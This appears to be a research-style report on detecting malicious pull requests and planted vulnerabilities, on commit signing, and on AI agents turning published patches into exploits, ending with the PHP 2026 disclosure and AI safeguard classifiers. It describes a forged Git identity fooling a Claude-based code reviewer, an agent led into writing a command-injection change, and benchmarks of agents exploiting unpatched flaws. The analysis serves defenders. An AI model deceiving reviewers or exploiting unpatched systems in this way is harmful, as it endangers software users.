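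| Result of the manual review | Repositories |
|---|---:|
| Confirmed as malicious | 564 |
| False alarms | 502 |
| Excluded because the project said it was for security testing, research or collecting malware | 487 |

Many of the false alarms were for remote-administration tools and system monitors. Remote-administration tools and backdoors both let someone run commands on a distant computer. They differ in whether the computer's owner agreed to it, which the extracted code may not show. System monitors may also run commands and collect information about the machine, as spyware does.

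The 487 excluded projects are harder to classify. The reviewers excluded them based on their README files, but a project's author writes its README, and a criminal can label a password stealer "for educational purposes only". Zhao and colleagues counted a repository as malicious only if its purpose was undeniable, so some of the excluded projects may also have been hostile.

If all the repositories that MalTotal passed were harmless, its false-alarm rate was about 0.4%, roughly 14 times the rate Datadog claims. Yet 36% of its alarms were confirmed, compared with 3% in the Datadog example, because malicious code was much more common. At least one in 213 of these repositories was malicious, while the example assumes one attack in 104,000 pull requests. In Zhao and colleagues' benchmark, between a third and half of the samples were malicious, and at least 93% of MalTotal's alarms were correct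 in each of the five programming languages.

### How often gates block genuine fixes

A false alarm on a security fix does more harm than most false alarms because users remain exposed while the fix is delayed. There seem to be no good data on how often this happens, and no published rate for gates in real projects.

The closest controlled test is in *Adaptive Code Revision Attacks on AI Pull Request Reviewers* (2026). It ran six versions of an AI reviewer on 33 past fixes by developers, and all 198 reviews approved the fix. This is encouraging, especially since the models that Alexopoulos and colleagues tested flagged most repaired files. Those models had to classify whether a long file contained any vulnerability, while these reviewers judged a specific repair. But 33 fixes is a small sample, and a reviewer that wrongly rejected one fix in 12 on average would still approve all 33 about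 6% of the time.

Records from real projects mostly concern human decisions. *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (2026) cites a large study in which maintainers often delayed or rejected security updates from Dependabot, a GitHub bot that proposes updates to vulnerable dependencies. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) examined security changes written by AI agents. A static analyser found flaws in the accepted changes from OpenAI's Codex but none in the rejected ones. Neither result shows that a security check blocked a good fix, since maintainers may have rejected changes for duplicating other work or breaking something.

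In *False positive detection of a vulnerability that has been fixed*, AgustinBettati reported a mistake of this kind, in which GitHub's dependency check still flagged a flaw after it was fixed. The project had specified the component by exact commit, and a developer replied that the tool had no good way to tell whether such a commit contained the fix. Specifying an exact commit is recommended security practice, and it protects users when an attacker moves version labels, as happened to tj-actions.

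AI reviewers also raise false alarms in ordinary code. *Through a Scanner Falsely* (Werrett, 2025) describes one that reported a nonexistent "CRITICAL VULNERABILITY" and thoroughly explained how attackers could take over accounts.

Blocked fixes probably leave few records because the developer rewrites the change or a maintainer overrides the scanner, and neither has much reason to report the block. A large project could measure how often its scanner blocks fixes by counting how many of the fixes later listed in security advisories were first flagged.

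### Why success on payloads does not carry over to planted vulnerabilities

According to Datadog's documentation, its scanner looks for "intent to cause harm (not accidental vulnerabilities)". This helps keep false alarms low, because developers introduce vulnerabilities by accident far more often than attackers submit payloads. But attackers who plant a vulnerability design it to look accidental, so a scanner that ignores apparent accidents will tend to miss it.

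Flagging every vulnerability would not identify the attackers either. If 1% of Datadog's 520,000 pull requests a year accidentally introduced a vulnerability, and attackers planted vulnerabilities in another five, a perfect vulnerability detector would flag 5,205 changes. Blocking them all would be right, but 99.9% of them would come from honest developers.

Datadog's success against the npm attacks is also weak evidence that it would catch planted flaws, because stolen tokens, encoded scripts and unfamiliar web addresses are visible in the code, while a planted vulnerability may consist only of a missing check. MalTotal would have particular trouble with such a flaw, since it starts by looking for sensitive operations and skips projects that contain none. Deleting the limit on wrong passwords from a login function, for example, adds no sensitive operation.

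Chen and colleagues tested two AI reviewers on 14 pull requests that lacked a necessary check. Each blocked nine, but CodeRabbit correctly identified a third as many flaws as the other. On 12 previously unknown vulnerabilities from real projects, CodeRabbit blocked ten changes but gave the right reason, with evidence, for only four. An author who relied on such a review might fix the wrong thing, as with the curl change in Yang and colleagues' tests.

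In the attack on Nx, a plainly hostile script stole the publishing token. The theft was possible because of an honest mistake by the project's own team in a title check, which passed review. An attacker preparing the theft could have contributed exactly the same diff for that check.

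## Tests of evidence from outside the diff: behaviour, context and identity

A gate needs evidence from outside the diff to judge the author of a change like the Nx title check. It can run the program and observe its behaviour, read the documents and conversations that surround the change, or check who sent the change.

### Lily: comparing what two versions do

A reviewer can easily overlook a hidden trigger in a long diff, but once someone activates it, the program usually has to do something it doesn't normally do. Kokkonis and colleagues built a tool called Lily around this idea. It monitors system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, start another program or use the network.

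Lily relies on fuzzing, a type of automatic testing. A fuzzer alters existing inputs at random, runs the program on the results, and keeps any input that reaches code no earlier input had reached. Some large projects already fuzz each new commit for about ten minutes to look for crashes. Lily uses the same ten minutes as follows:

1. It runs the new version of the program on inputs saved from fuzzing earlier versions, and records which types of system call each input causes. These sets of calls define the program's normal behaviour.
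2. It fuzzes the new version and records the same information for each input that the fuzzer keeps.
3. If an input causes a set of calls that is not among the normal ones, Lily runs the old version on that input. If the old version makes the same calls, the change is not responsible. Otherwise Lily raises an alarm.
4. It finds the changed lines that the program ran on that input, picks out those that led to the unusual calls, and shows them to the maintainer together with the input.

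The altered vsFTPd release from 2011 differed from the previous official one by 1,407 lines in five files. When Lily tests it, the fuzzer eventually tries a user name that contains ":)". The program then waits for a network connection and starts a shell, a combination of calls that none of the saved inputs causes. The old version does not do this when given the same name. Lily's report narrows the 1,407 lines to seven.

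Lily's report doesn't assess intent, but it can help a person judge it. Few honest authors would make a file server open an administrator's shell when it receives a smiley.

#### Results on safe and backdoored changes

Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on 13 open-source programs from a collection of backdoors that they had published earlier. Three of the backdoors came from the real attacks on PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd, and the other ten were synthetic. Because fuzzing is partly random, the team ran Lily 20 times on every change:

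| Changes | Runs | Runs with an alarm | Share |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| 13 backdoored commits | 260 | 233 | 90% |
| 50 backdoored releases | 1,000 | 828 | 83% |
| 432 safe commits | 8,640 | 17 | 0.2% |
| 50 safe releases | 1,000 | 43 | 4.3% |

Lily caught each backdoored change in at least one of its 20 runs, but a project would probably run it only once per change and should expect to miss some.

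A few unusual changes caused most of the false alarms. Four large merges in PHP caused 12 of the 17 false alarms on commits. Two releases of the sound library libsndfile set off an alarm in every run, accounting for 40 of the 43 false alarms on releases. Counting only the 337 safe commits that affected code would raise the false-alarm rate, but only to 0.25%.

The low false-alarm rate depends on requiring behaviour to be both new and untypical. When the researchers made Lily flag all new behaviour, it raised false alarms in 10% of runs on safe commits and 58% of runs on safe releases, because legitimate updates often add behaviour. When it flagged all untypical behaviour, the figures were 14% and 20%, because programs have old features that rarely run.

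#### Attacks that leave no trace in system calls

Lily cannot judge code that the fuzzer never runs. In the 337 commits that affected code, the fuzzer reached an average of about 32% of the changed lines. The main reason was that the harness, a small program that developers write to feed inputs to the software, often covered only part of that software. Kokkonis and colleagues found that modern harnesses usually reach nearly all the changed code. But the fuzzer could reach every backdoor in their test, so the 90% figure is weak evidence about backdoors elsewhere in a program.

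Some attacks would escape notice even if the fuzzer ran the code. The login function that lost its limit on wrong passwords now checks the sixth password with the same types of system call as the first, so Lily would classify the input as safe. A new Dual_EC constant changes the numbers that a program generates but not the system calls it makes. A use-after-free flaw like those in Wu and Lu's patches may cause no unusual calls until somebody exploits it, though an ordinary fuzzer might find it by crashing the program.

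Lily also covers only the program under test, so it misses payloads that run in an installation script or an automated job, such as the altered publishing script at Nx.

So Lily is well suited to finding explicit backdoors, like the eleven that Thomas and Francillon examined in routers and cameras, but poorly suited to finding most planted vulnerabilities. It also compares each version with the one before, so it will not find a backdoor that was already in the program when the project began using Lily. Kokkonis and colleagues recommend a separate, slower audit for such backdoors.

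### Predicting a developer's purpose without the code

New behaviour is only a problem if it breaks a requirement or if nobody wanted it. In *From Code Review to Code Critique*, Maddila, Rashik and colleagues at Meta (2026) try to infer what a developer wanted by using the material around a change. Their system is for code that AI agents write at a developer's request. The paper distinguishes the purpose of a change from a summary of it. For example, "Added a 5-second timeout" to a call to another service is a summary, while the purpose is to stop the application from hanging when that service does not respond.

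A language model predicts a code change's purpose from the developer's conversation with the AI agent, the change's title, summary and test plan, and any linked plans or documents. It does not see the code, because if it did, it could describe what the code does and present that as the purpose.

The researchers tested this on 121 changes whose purposes a member of the team had written down by hand. They used another model to check which predictions matched those purposes. With a single prompt, the system had an F1 of 0.844. An agent that could look up more context reached 0.860 but processed over six times as much text. In everyday use, engineers approved 101 of the 112 predictions they rated.

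The system then checks whether the code fits the purpose. One model reads the diff, without its summary or the conversation, and lists what the change does. Another compares this list with the predicted purpose and scores the difference, which the paper calls drift, from 0 to 100. On 118 changes, the score differed from a human annotator's by about 10 points on average. The model was good at recognising changes that matched their purpose completely (F1 of 0.89) or hardly at all (0.81), but poor at recognising "moderate" drift (0.34).

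A high score is a useful warning to an honest developer whose AI agent has misunderstood the task or added something nobody asked for. But the system takes the developer's own words as the standard. Suppose a hostile developer tells an agent to replace `execFileSync` with `execSync` in `lookUp` so that the output can go to a file. The agent does that, the predicted purpose matches the code, and the drift is close to zero. The score is correct because the code does what the developer requested, but visitors can now run commands on the server.

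This assumption of honesty matters because Meta lets some authors merge their changes without prior review by a colleague if the drift is low and the system finds nothing else to inspect. Maddila and colleagues have traced no defects to these changes, although developers later reverted 0.33% of them, compared with 0.17% of ordinary changes. Meta knows who its engineers are and can hold them to account. An open-source project that offered strangers the same shortcut would rely on attackers to state their purpose truthfully. Such a project would also seldom have the conversation between the author and the AI agent.

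### Tests generated from the inferred purpose

Becker and colleagues at Meta use a change's inferred purpose to decide what to test. A language model reads the change's code, title and summary, guesses what the developer is trying to do, and lists ways the attempt could go wrong. For each risk, the system adds that mistake to a copy of the old program. It then writes a test that passes on the old program and fails on the broken copy, and runs the test on the proposed change. If the test fails there too, the developer may have made that mistake.

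The team compared this with a simpler method that ignores the purpose and looks for any test that passes on the old version and fails on the new one. The method based on purpose produced such a test for 49 of 617 code changes (7.9%), and the simpler one for 26 of 654 (4.0%). These figures include both intended and unintended changes in behaviour. The paper does not say which method found the eight bugs that engineers confirmed, so it is unclear whether guessing the purpose helped to find real bugs or only more differences in behaviour.

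Knowing the purpose of a change helps most when it rules something out. One of the system's rules treats any new behaviour as suspicious if the developer only meant to refactor, which should leave behaviour unchanged. Others apply the same reasoning to the removal of unused code and to changes that should only add something, such as logging. These rules could also expose a false description. SEVRA-BENCH's hostile change to a shell call, described as "API normalization", would break the first rule if the system wrote a test with the right input. Such rules don't help when an attacker openly announces the new behaviour and gives a plausible reason for it, because the behaviour then matches the stated purpose.

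Asking authors whether they intended the new behaviour, as the team did, also relies on honesty. An engineer who has made a mistake will be glad to be asked, but an attacker will answer yes. In some cases the team also asked the change's reviewers. In a project that accepts code from strangers, a maintainer who knows the security requirements would be better to ask than the author.

### A forged author name

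If the value of a description depends on the author's honesty, a gate might reasonably trust authors with a good reputation more, but it must first verify who the author is. The Register's *Git identity spoof fools Claude into giving bad code the nod* (April 2026) described how researchers used two Git commands to put a trusted developer's name on a malicious change, which an automated reviewer running on Anthropic's Claude then approved.

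SC Media's *AI code reviewer fooled by spoofed developer identity* adds that the researchers, from Manifold Security, had set up the review process to automatically approve requests from "recognized industry legends". The model was following this bad rule when it accepted the false name, so the demonstration does not show how much a famous name would have helped without the rule. Information about the author did, however, shift some models' verdicts in Shahriar and colleagues' tests.

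Git makes the name easy to forge. *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult* (Holtgrave, Friedrich and colleagues, 2025) distinguishes three roles. The author writes a change, the committer records it as a commit, and the pusher uploads it to a site such as GitHub. Author and committer names can be false, as the 2021 attack on PHP showed. Only the pusher has to log in, and GitHub's commit page does not show who that was. It links instead to the profiles of the accounts that use the email addresses in the commit. The researchers pushed a commit of their own that GitHub displayed as the work of its update bot, Dependabot.

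A gate could check whether the person who pushed a commit is its named author, but a mismatch is usually innocent. Developers often merge each other's work, and many projects use bots to push it. Of 437,211 commits that Holtgrave and colleagues collected in 2024, only 30% had the same account as author, committer and pusher.

### What a signed commit proves

A digital signature is much harder to forge than a name. The signer has a private key, which stays secret, and publishes a matching public key. Git can use the private key to sign a commit's contents, including its files, message and names. Anyone with the public key can then check that the holder of the private key signed exactly this commit. How much that proves about the author depends on what else has gone wrong:

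| Evidence of identity | What it establishes | If someone steals the account or key | If the maintainer is hostile |
|---|---|---|---|
| Name and email address | Nothing by itself | The thief does not even need the account | The name is genuine |
| Valid signature | Someone with the private key signed this commit | A thief with the key can produce one | The signature is valid |
| GitHub's signature on an edit made through its website | Someone logged in to the account made the edit | A thief with the account can obtain one | The signature is valid |

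Across 50,328 widely used projects, Holtgrave and colleagues found that 95.4% of committers had never signed a commit and only 2.0% had signed all of theirs. A missing signature is therefore hardly evidence against an author, unless that person normally signs everything. A failed signature check is also weak evidence. GitHub could not verify about 18% of the signatures that users made with PGP, the most common method, usually because it did not have the public key.

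The signature also comes from the committer, who may not be the author. According to GitHub's *About commit signature verification*, when the two differ, GitHub labels the commit "Partially verified" only if the named author has turned on an optional setting called vigilant mode. Otherwise, GitHub labels the commit "Verified" as long as the signature is valid.

#### Stolen accounts and stolen build systems

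Someone who breaks into a GitHub account may not need the owner's private key to make commits labelled "Verified", because GitHub signs edits made through its website. If a thief steals a key, the label stays on the thief's commits even after the owner revokes the key. GitHub permanently records the result of its first check so that honest commits remain verified when developers replace their keys or leave. The record includes the time of the check, which investigators can compare with the time of the theft.

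Packages can also carry signatures, and a May 2026 attack on TanStack, a group of JavaScript packages on npm, showed that these have the same limitation. SLSA's *Mini Shai-Hulud* (2026) analyses the attack. SLSA is a set of standards for recording how software was built. A signed record of this kind, called provenance, identifies the build system and source code used to produce a package.

The attackers published 84 malicious package files under 42 TanStack names, all with valid provenance that named the correct repository and publishing job. They had run their own code inside the genuine publishing job, where they took the token that let it sign and publish. Provenance stops an impostor who has no access to a project's build system, but these attackers had that access.

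According to SLSA, a build system that kept its jobs properly separate would have prevented this attack. Even then, the signature would show only that the system had faithfully built the package from its source code, which could itself be malicious. A better clue was that both jobs that published the malicious packages were marked as failed. An alert for packages published by failed jobs could have exposed the attack within minutes. Like Lily, it would have responded to odd behaviour even though the identity checks passed.

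#### A trusted maintainer with a valid key

Signatures stop other people from impersonating a trusted developer, but they do not show that the developer deserves that trust. A hostile maintainer does not need to impersonate anyone. A signature from Jia Tan on the malicious XZ Utils commits would have correctly shown that they came from Jia Tan.

Signatures become more useful once someone has discovered an attack. If a maintainer always signs their changes, colleagues can find every change signed with the same key and review it again.

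Holtgrave and colleagues conclude that maintainers would ideally judge only the code, not who sent it, as the Linux developers largely did when they re-reviewed the University of Minnesota's commits. But they acknowledge that many volunteers lack the time for this. Reputation saves maintainers time by letting them read familiar contributors' work less closely, which also helps a hostile insider.

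### What practitioners look for

On 15 September 2025, ten practitioners from eight companies met three researchers to discuss attacks on the software supply chain, meaning the outside code and tools that go into a product. Participants found it very hard to determine intent from a single commit, and suggested also considering the contributor's history and the change's later effects. *S3C2 Summit 2025-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2026) summarises the discussion without attributing comments to individuals. It reports the opinion of a small group and contains no measurements.

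The participants also suggested looking for odd behaviour by contributors, such as commits at unusual hours, edits to unexpected files or a sudden change of keys. They treated these as hints that a change needs a closer look. That seems right, since observers misread some of the odd time zones in XZ's history.

Researchers have built tools that look for such patterns automatically. One by Ganz and colleagues detected 15 of 19 attacks, with an average false-alarm rate of 10.75%, according to Kokkonis and colleagues. That is more than 50 times Lily's rate on commits, although the two teams used mostly different projects and attacks. Another tool, Anomalicious, had a low false-alarm rate but detected only 53% of repositories infected with malware, according to Holtgrave and colleagues.

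Some of the practitioners' other measures do not depend on judging the author. One is to require two people to review each pull request, so that a hostile or careless maintainer cannot approve a change alone. This is difficult for projects with only one active maintainer, and an attacker may also win over the second reviewer. Another measure is to cut off a build job's network access once it has downloaded what it needs. A payload in the build could still run, but it could not send stolen passwords to an outside address. Participants considered this more reliable than reputation scores.

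#### Reviewing what a change newly allows

A newer proposal from the summit is to show reviewers how a change alters the software's capabilities, such as whether it can now read more files, start other programs or use the network. Applied to some of the earlier examples, such a review might show the following:

| Change | New capability |
|---|---|
| Installation script that steals passwords | Reads saved passwords and contacts an outside address |
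| PHP's "Fix typo" commit | Runs code from a web request |
| Unsafe version of `lookUp` | Starts a shell, where it used to start only nslookup |
| Login function without its limit on wrong passwords | None |
| New constant for Dual_EC | None |

This would make false descriptions like the one in the PHP attack easy to spot. The reviewer could reject the change for its false description without working out who wrote it or why. For `lookUp`, the result depends on how detailed the list is. If the function's entry were only "starts other programs", the safe and unsafe versions would look the same. The last two changes would pass unnoticed, as they would with Lily, because they weaken a protection without giving the program anything new to do.

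Rahman and colleagues report no test of the proposal. The closest evidence comes from the version of Lily that flagged all new behaviour, which raised far more false alarms than the full tool. If capability reviews raised false alarms as often, a project could use them to prompt questions from reviewers but could hardly block every change they flagged.

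## Published fixes and AI safeguards: repair and attack use the same knowledge

Even a fix from an honest author can put people in danger for a while, because it shows attackers what is wrong with the version that most users are still running.

### Why a fix points to the flaw

A typical repair in the language C might look like this:

```diff
 void saveName(const char *name) {
   char space[64];
+  if (strlen(name) >= sizeof space) return;
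   strcpy(space, name);
 }
```

The function copies a name into a 64-byte buffer, and the new line rejects names that do not fit. Anyone who reads that line can learn that older versions accept such names and write past the end of the buffer, which may let an attacker take control of the program. Someone who had never heard of the flaw now knows which function to attack and what sort of input to use.

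Many users receive only the compiled program, but an attacker can compare its old and new versions too. In *Automatic Patch-Based Exploit Generation is Possible* (2008), Brumley, Poosankam and colleagues described the general problem of taking a program and its patched version and automatically generating an exploit for the flaw that the patch removed. They did this for five Microsoft programs, using patches from Windows Update. According to jad-reads' *Thoughts on Automatic Patch-Based Exploit Generation is Possible* (2009), the method handled only fixes that check a program's input, like the one above, but could produce an exploit in minutes.

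In *Automatic patch-based exploit generation* (2008), Errata Security objected to the word "exploit", arguing that turning a patch into a fully working attack takes many steps and that the researchers had automated only one of them, in certain cases. Hackers had been doing all the steps by hand for years.

Brumley and colleagues' practical warning did not depend on that dispute. Windows Update delivered each patch over a long period, so people who received it early could attack those who were still waiting.

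### What AI agents can do with a fix

AI agents can now carry out the steps that the 2008 method left to people. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) cites an early result in which an agent running on GPT-4 exploited 87% of a set of disclosed vulnerabilities, while GPT-3.5 and commercial scanners exploited none.

*CyberBinGym* (Wijayadi, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on compiled updates, using 100 old vulnerabilities from 53 widely used projects. Each agent received the program before and after the fix, without source code or any description of the flaw. It had to find an input that crashed the old version but not the new one, then break into a server running the old version and read a secret file.

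| Agent | Triggered the flaw | Read the secret file | Average cost per task | Average time per task |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| GPT-5.6 in Codex | 88% | 20% | $28 | 2.1 hours |
| Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code | 85% | 6% | $15 | 1.3 hours |
| Kimi K3 in Kimi Code | 64% | 0% | $38 | 5.8 hours |

Having the fixed version helped the agents. On 20 of the tasks, Codex triggered 11 flaws with only the old version and 18 with both, and its successful break-ins rose from two to five. These numbers are small, but the researchers also read the records of all 26 successful attacks in the main test. In 17 of them, differences between the versions had led the agent directly to the flaw it used.

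Exploiting a flaw is still much harder than triggering it, and common defences make it even harder. Codex broke into 20 programs, but when the researchers rebuilt those programs with standard protections against memory attacks, it succeeded on only two.

Android phones run a version of Linux, and Linux fixes reach them late. In *Aftershock*, Shehada and Qian (2026) gave an agent running on GPT-5.6 sol a public Linux fix and asked it to attack an Android system that still lacked the fix. They kept the normal defences on throughout and counted an exploit only if an ordinary app could use it to take full control of a fresh simulated phone. The agent could not search the web for published exploits.

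| Stage | Flaws remaining |
|---|---:|
| Linux vulnerabilities published from January 2024 to September 2026 | 10,301 |
| In code that an ordinary Android app might reach | 1,233 |
| Likely to corrupt memory or leak information | 612 |
| Judged to be present and reachable in a suitable Android version | 152 |
| Triggered from an ordinary app | 38 |
| Exploited to take full control | 17 |

The successful attacks took a median of 14.3 hours of the agent's time and $321. Including screening and all the failed attempts, each exploit cost $1,692. Most of the 21 failures at the last stage were runs that reached their $1,250 spending limit, so an attacker with a larger budget might have had more success. The agent also adapted nine of the exploits to real Pixel phones with unpatched software, and 12 of 14 such trials worked.

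In the eight flaw-and-phone combinations where a fix arrived during the study, the fix took a median of 181 days to get from Linux to the phone. Eight is a small sample, but even a delay several times shorter would give an attacker plenty of time. Only three of the 17 exploited flaws appeared in Android's security bulletins, which suggests the people responsible for Android had trouble telling which Linux fixes mattered. Shehada and Qian point out that maintainers could use the same system to identify those fixes.

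### PHP, October 2026

In October 2026 PHP's developers had to publish a fix for two flaws, and they expected attackers to read it at once. Under the right conditions, either flaw could let a stranger run code on a web server. Both were more than a decade old and were apparently honest mistakes, unlike the backdoor that an intruder put into PHP's repository in 2021.

The PHP Foundation's *Today's PHP Security Release, and How We're Strengthening PHP Security* (2026) reports that a developer saw the first signs of the main problem in 2024. Nobody could find a practical way to attack it, every proposed fix had drawbacks, and the work stalled repeatedly. On 11 August 2026, the security firm Calif reported a way to run code on a server, and OpenAI independently reported the same underlying problem the same day. Fixing it then became the team's top priority.

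The repair touched 390 files (Daubois, 2026, *What the PHP2Shell rumors got wrong, from inside the PHP security team*). Publishing it was complicated because the PHP project releases only source code, which Debian, Red Hat and others turn into the packages people install. The PHP team therefore gave these distributors the fix early under an embargo, an agreement to keep it secret until a common release time. Volker Dusch, who worked on the release, said in an interview that anyone could now turn a patch, or even a compiled program, into an exploit much faster than before (Barnes, 2026, *Volker Dusch on the PHP RCE Vulnerabilities and Disclosure*).

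The secret came out shortly before the planned date:

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 17 October | Amazon recorded an attempted attack |
| 20 October, about 15:00 | The flaws' CVE numbers began to circulate online |
| 20 October, 21:57 | A decoy server received a request that resembled an attack |
| 21 October, 07:41 | Chainguard, one of the distributors, published its fixed builds |
| 21 October, 13:35 | PHP's release manager pushed the fix to the public repositories |
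| 21 October, 14:00 | PHP announced the flaws, a day earlier than planned |

Chainguard's early release recreated the problem Brumley and colleagues had described. For more than six hours, anyone could study the repaired program while most other distributors' users could not yet install it. An average Codex run in Wijayadi and colleagues' tests took about two hours, so six hours could be enough time to build an exploit, although most of those runs failed to produce a working one.

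*Chainguard Broke the php2shell Embargo* (Barnes, 2026) summarises a post in which Chainguard's chief executive, Dan Lorenc, defended the decision. Lorenc said that other companies had seen working exploits in use, and that Chainguard had found the flaw with very little effort. On 16 October, one of the original researchers had told Chainguard that something was coming in PHP. That night, its staff found the same problem with their own tools, an AI model and a basic prompt. Nils Adermann of the PHP Foundation replied that people had only been probing for the flaw, and the security team had identified no functional exploit by the time of the release.

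Arghire (2026) reports in *PHP2Shell Exploitation Started Days Before Patches* that attack attempts multiplied soon after the fix came out. But nine days later, Whittaker (2026) concluded in *PHP had a rough week for security, but the pain isn't over yet* that a wave of mass website hacks had largely been averted.

The case is weak evidence that attackers learned from the fix. InfoQ's *PHP Patches Two Critical RCE Flaws That Were Already Under Attack* (2026) dates the attempt that Amazon recorded to four days before the patches, too early for the attacker to have learned from them. The first suspicious request in OffSeq's *PHP2Shell in the wild* (2026) also came too early, and OffSeq's decoys could not have shown whether any attack would have worked. Several groups had also found the problem independently. The case does show how much the fear of attacks learned from a fix now shapes repair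 work. The developers worked on the fix in private for weeks and published it 25 minutes before the announcement, so nobody outside a small circle could review it beforehand.

### Attack code in an honest fix

Maintainers need attack code even before they start a repair. Daubois (2026), in *How the PHP Security Team Handles Your Reports*, explains that no report gets a verdict until a team member has read it and tried to reproduce the flaw. Between July and mid-October, the team published 15 vulnerabilities and dealt with more than 100 reports that were invalid, duplicates or impossible to reproduce. According to Dusch, several of the PHP attacks that people showed off on social media were misleading because they worked only against a specially modified copy of the software.

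After the repair, the same attack can become a regression test, like the `lookUp` test that tried to create a file. The test fails on the old version, passes on the new one, and fails again if anybody reintroduces the flaw. Wijayadi and colleagues scored their agents in almost the same way, counting an input only if it crashed the old version but not the new one. In 88 of their 100 tasks, Codex produced a file that could have served as the first step of an attack or as a test for the fix.

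A test of this kind would also catch many of the reversed fixes in SEVRA-BENCH, however the author described the change, as long as the gate ran the test and blocked the author from deleting it. This is a strong reason to keep attack code in a project.

A public test also shows attackers how to trigger the flaw. A project can withhold the test until most users have updated, but until then outsiders have to trust the maintainers that the fix works. Publishing the test helps attackers less than it may seem, because a test usually needs only to trigger the flaw, and most of the agents that triggered a flaw got no further.

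A passing test shows only that one attack has stopped working. Dusch said of the PHP flaws, "We have to fix every place where this happens." *PHP Patches Seven Critical RCE Vulnerabilities* (Arghire, 2026) reports that the project patched seven more critical vulnerabilities in November, and that one of the patches finished an incomplete fix from October. On PHP Architect's *The PHP Podcast 2026.10.22* (2026), the hosts had worried about incomplete fixes because they show attackers where to look while leaving them a way in.

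A gate can judge attack code in a test by running the test in isolation on the code before and after the change. If the test fails on the old version and passes on the new one, the author's claim to have fixed something is true. This doesn't check the rest of the change, which might contain a payload, as the working fix for myNetwork did. The gate still needs to reject unreadable test files that come without a generator program, like those that hid the XZ backdoor.

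### Fixes disguised as routine work

A maintainer may be tempted to disguise a fix if it would show attackers where to look. The Linux developers were long criticised for repairing security flaws in small commits with bland messages and no announcement. Other projects hid their fixes among renamed variables and moved code, hoping attackers would lose patience.

Louis Nyffenegger (2026), founder of the security training company PentesterLab, argues that such clutter no longer works because language models do not get tired of reading. He suggests that maintainers may need "cover stories", which present fixes as optimisation, refactoring or routine cleanup, but says he does not know the right solution.

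The evidence supports his point about clutter. In tests by Wijayadi and colleagues, the updates changed a median of 1,003 lines of source code across about 30 files, but agents that saw only the compiled result still triggered most of the flaws.

It is uncertain whether a false explanation would do better, but it cannot help much once an attacker has decided to study a particular fix, because even a true description of the flaw made little difference to agents that had both versions of the code. When Wijayadi and colleagues tested this on 50 tasks, Codex triggered 43 flaws with the description and 45 without it.

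A false description could still keep an attacker from noticing the fix. Linux receives more than 200 changes a day, and trained classifiers miss most unannounced fixes when set to keep false alarms low. But large language models make a broad search affordable. Shehada and Qian looked only at fixes with CVE numbers, but they estimate that the first AI screening of all the Linux changes from the same 33 months, over 200,000, would have cost about $15,000. False descriptions mislead review agents, so they might also mislead an attacker's agent, at least until the attacker thinks to hide the description from it.

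Disguising security fixes has an uncertain benefit, but it definitely makes descriptions less useful for detecting attacks. Suppose that a gate compares each change with its description and finds ten mismatches in one year. Nine are careless and one belongs to an attack, so a mismatch has a 10% chance of being hostile. If the maintainers also disguise 40 security fixes as cleanup, the gate finds 50 mismatches, still with one attack among them, and the chance falls to 2%.

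The damage would be worst among trusted insiders. A stranger has no legitimate reason to disguise a fix, so a false description from one would remain about as suspicious as before. But a developer who noticed that a colleague's "cleanup" changed how a program checks its input would have a reason to say nothing, because a public question might reveal the fix. That habit would have helped Jia Tan, who gave a plausible technical reason for replacing the XZ test files. Becker and colleagues' automated system treats new behaviour in a supposed refactoring as suspicious, but a project that often disguised its fixes would have to exempt its maintainers from such a rule.

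Users and distributors also suffer, because they cannot prioritize a fix they mistake for code cleanup. Android's maintainers already seem to miss important Linux fixes that have public CVE numbers.

An automated review that judged a code change by its effect on the program would mistake fixes for attacks, and attacks for fixes, less often, because a disguised fix makes the program safer and a disguised attack makes it more dangerous. This helps only when the review has the security requirement to check the change against.

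Maintainers can gain time in better ways than by describing a fix falsely. They can prepare the fix in private and publish it with the release, as PHP did. If they must publish it earlier, they can describe the change accurately without mentioning security. For example, "Reject names longer than 63 characters" is true and draws little attention. This omission gives attackers slightly more information than a false description would, but it lets reviewers keep treating false descriptions as a sign that something is wrong.

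### Safeguards inside AI models

The companies that run AI models face the same problem when a user submits code and asks for help. A gate in front of the model has to decide from the request whether to allow it, and most requests about a vulnerability have both an honest and a hostile use:

| Request | Why a defender would make it | How an attacker could use the answer |
|---|---|---|
| Find a flaw in this code | To repair it | To attack people who run the code |
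| Explain what this fix changed | To decide how urgently to update | To attack people who have not updated |
| Write a test that triggers the flaw | To check the repair | As the first step of an exploit |
| Build a working exploit | To show how serious the flaw is | To break into a system |

A user's explanation of why they want the answer is about as reliable as a stranger's pull request description, because an attacker can type "I maintain this project" as easily as a maintainer can.

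Anthropic sells its strongest model in two versions with different safeguards. One of them, Claude Fable 5.2, is available to everyone, and separate classifiers check users' requests. Pogorelec (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior*, reports that the classifiers block high-risk cybersecurity tasks, such as generating exploits and penetration testing. An older model, Claude Opus 4.8, then answers instead, so an honest user whose request is blocked by mistake still gets some help, though from a weaker model. When a model refuses outright, the refusal may reveal that the code contains a flaw, as CrowdStrike's *When AI Guardrails Expose Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes.

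#### What a fall in blocked requests shows

When Anthropic first tested Fable 5.2, the classifiers blocked roughly 55% fewer requests than those for Fable 5.1 had. Blocks on cybersecurity fell by about 60% and those on biology by about 40%. The company says the safeguards are as robust as before.

The drop in blocks is good news for defenders only if that last claim is true, and the percentages cannot confirm it. Suppose the old classifier blocked 1,000 cybersecurity requests, 900 of them legitimate and 100 hostile. A 60% fall leaves 400 blocks. If the new classifier still stops all 100 hostile requests, it blocks only 300 legitimate ones. But if it blocks 60% fewer requests of both kinds, it blocks 360 legitimate requests and 40 hostile ones, letting through 60 hostile requests that the old one would have stopped. Both cases fit the published figure. Telling them apart requires the detection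 rate and the false-alarm rate, measured on requests whose purpose is known.

Such a set of requests is hard to build because people with opposite purposes can send identical requests, just as they can submit identical diffs.

#### Where a model could draw the line

One option is to help find and trigger flaws but refuse to write full exploits. Most repairs need only a trigger. Agents also seem more useful for repair than for attack at present. *LLM-Based Agents for Software and Systems Security* (2026) cites the BountyBench benchmark, in which leading agents were notably better at patching than at exploitation. Refusing exploits would therefore withhold the step that attackers find hardest while still giving defenders most of what they need.

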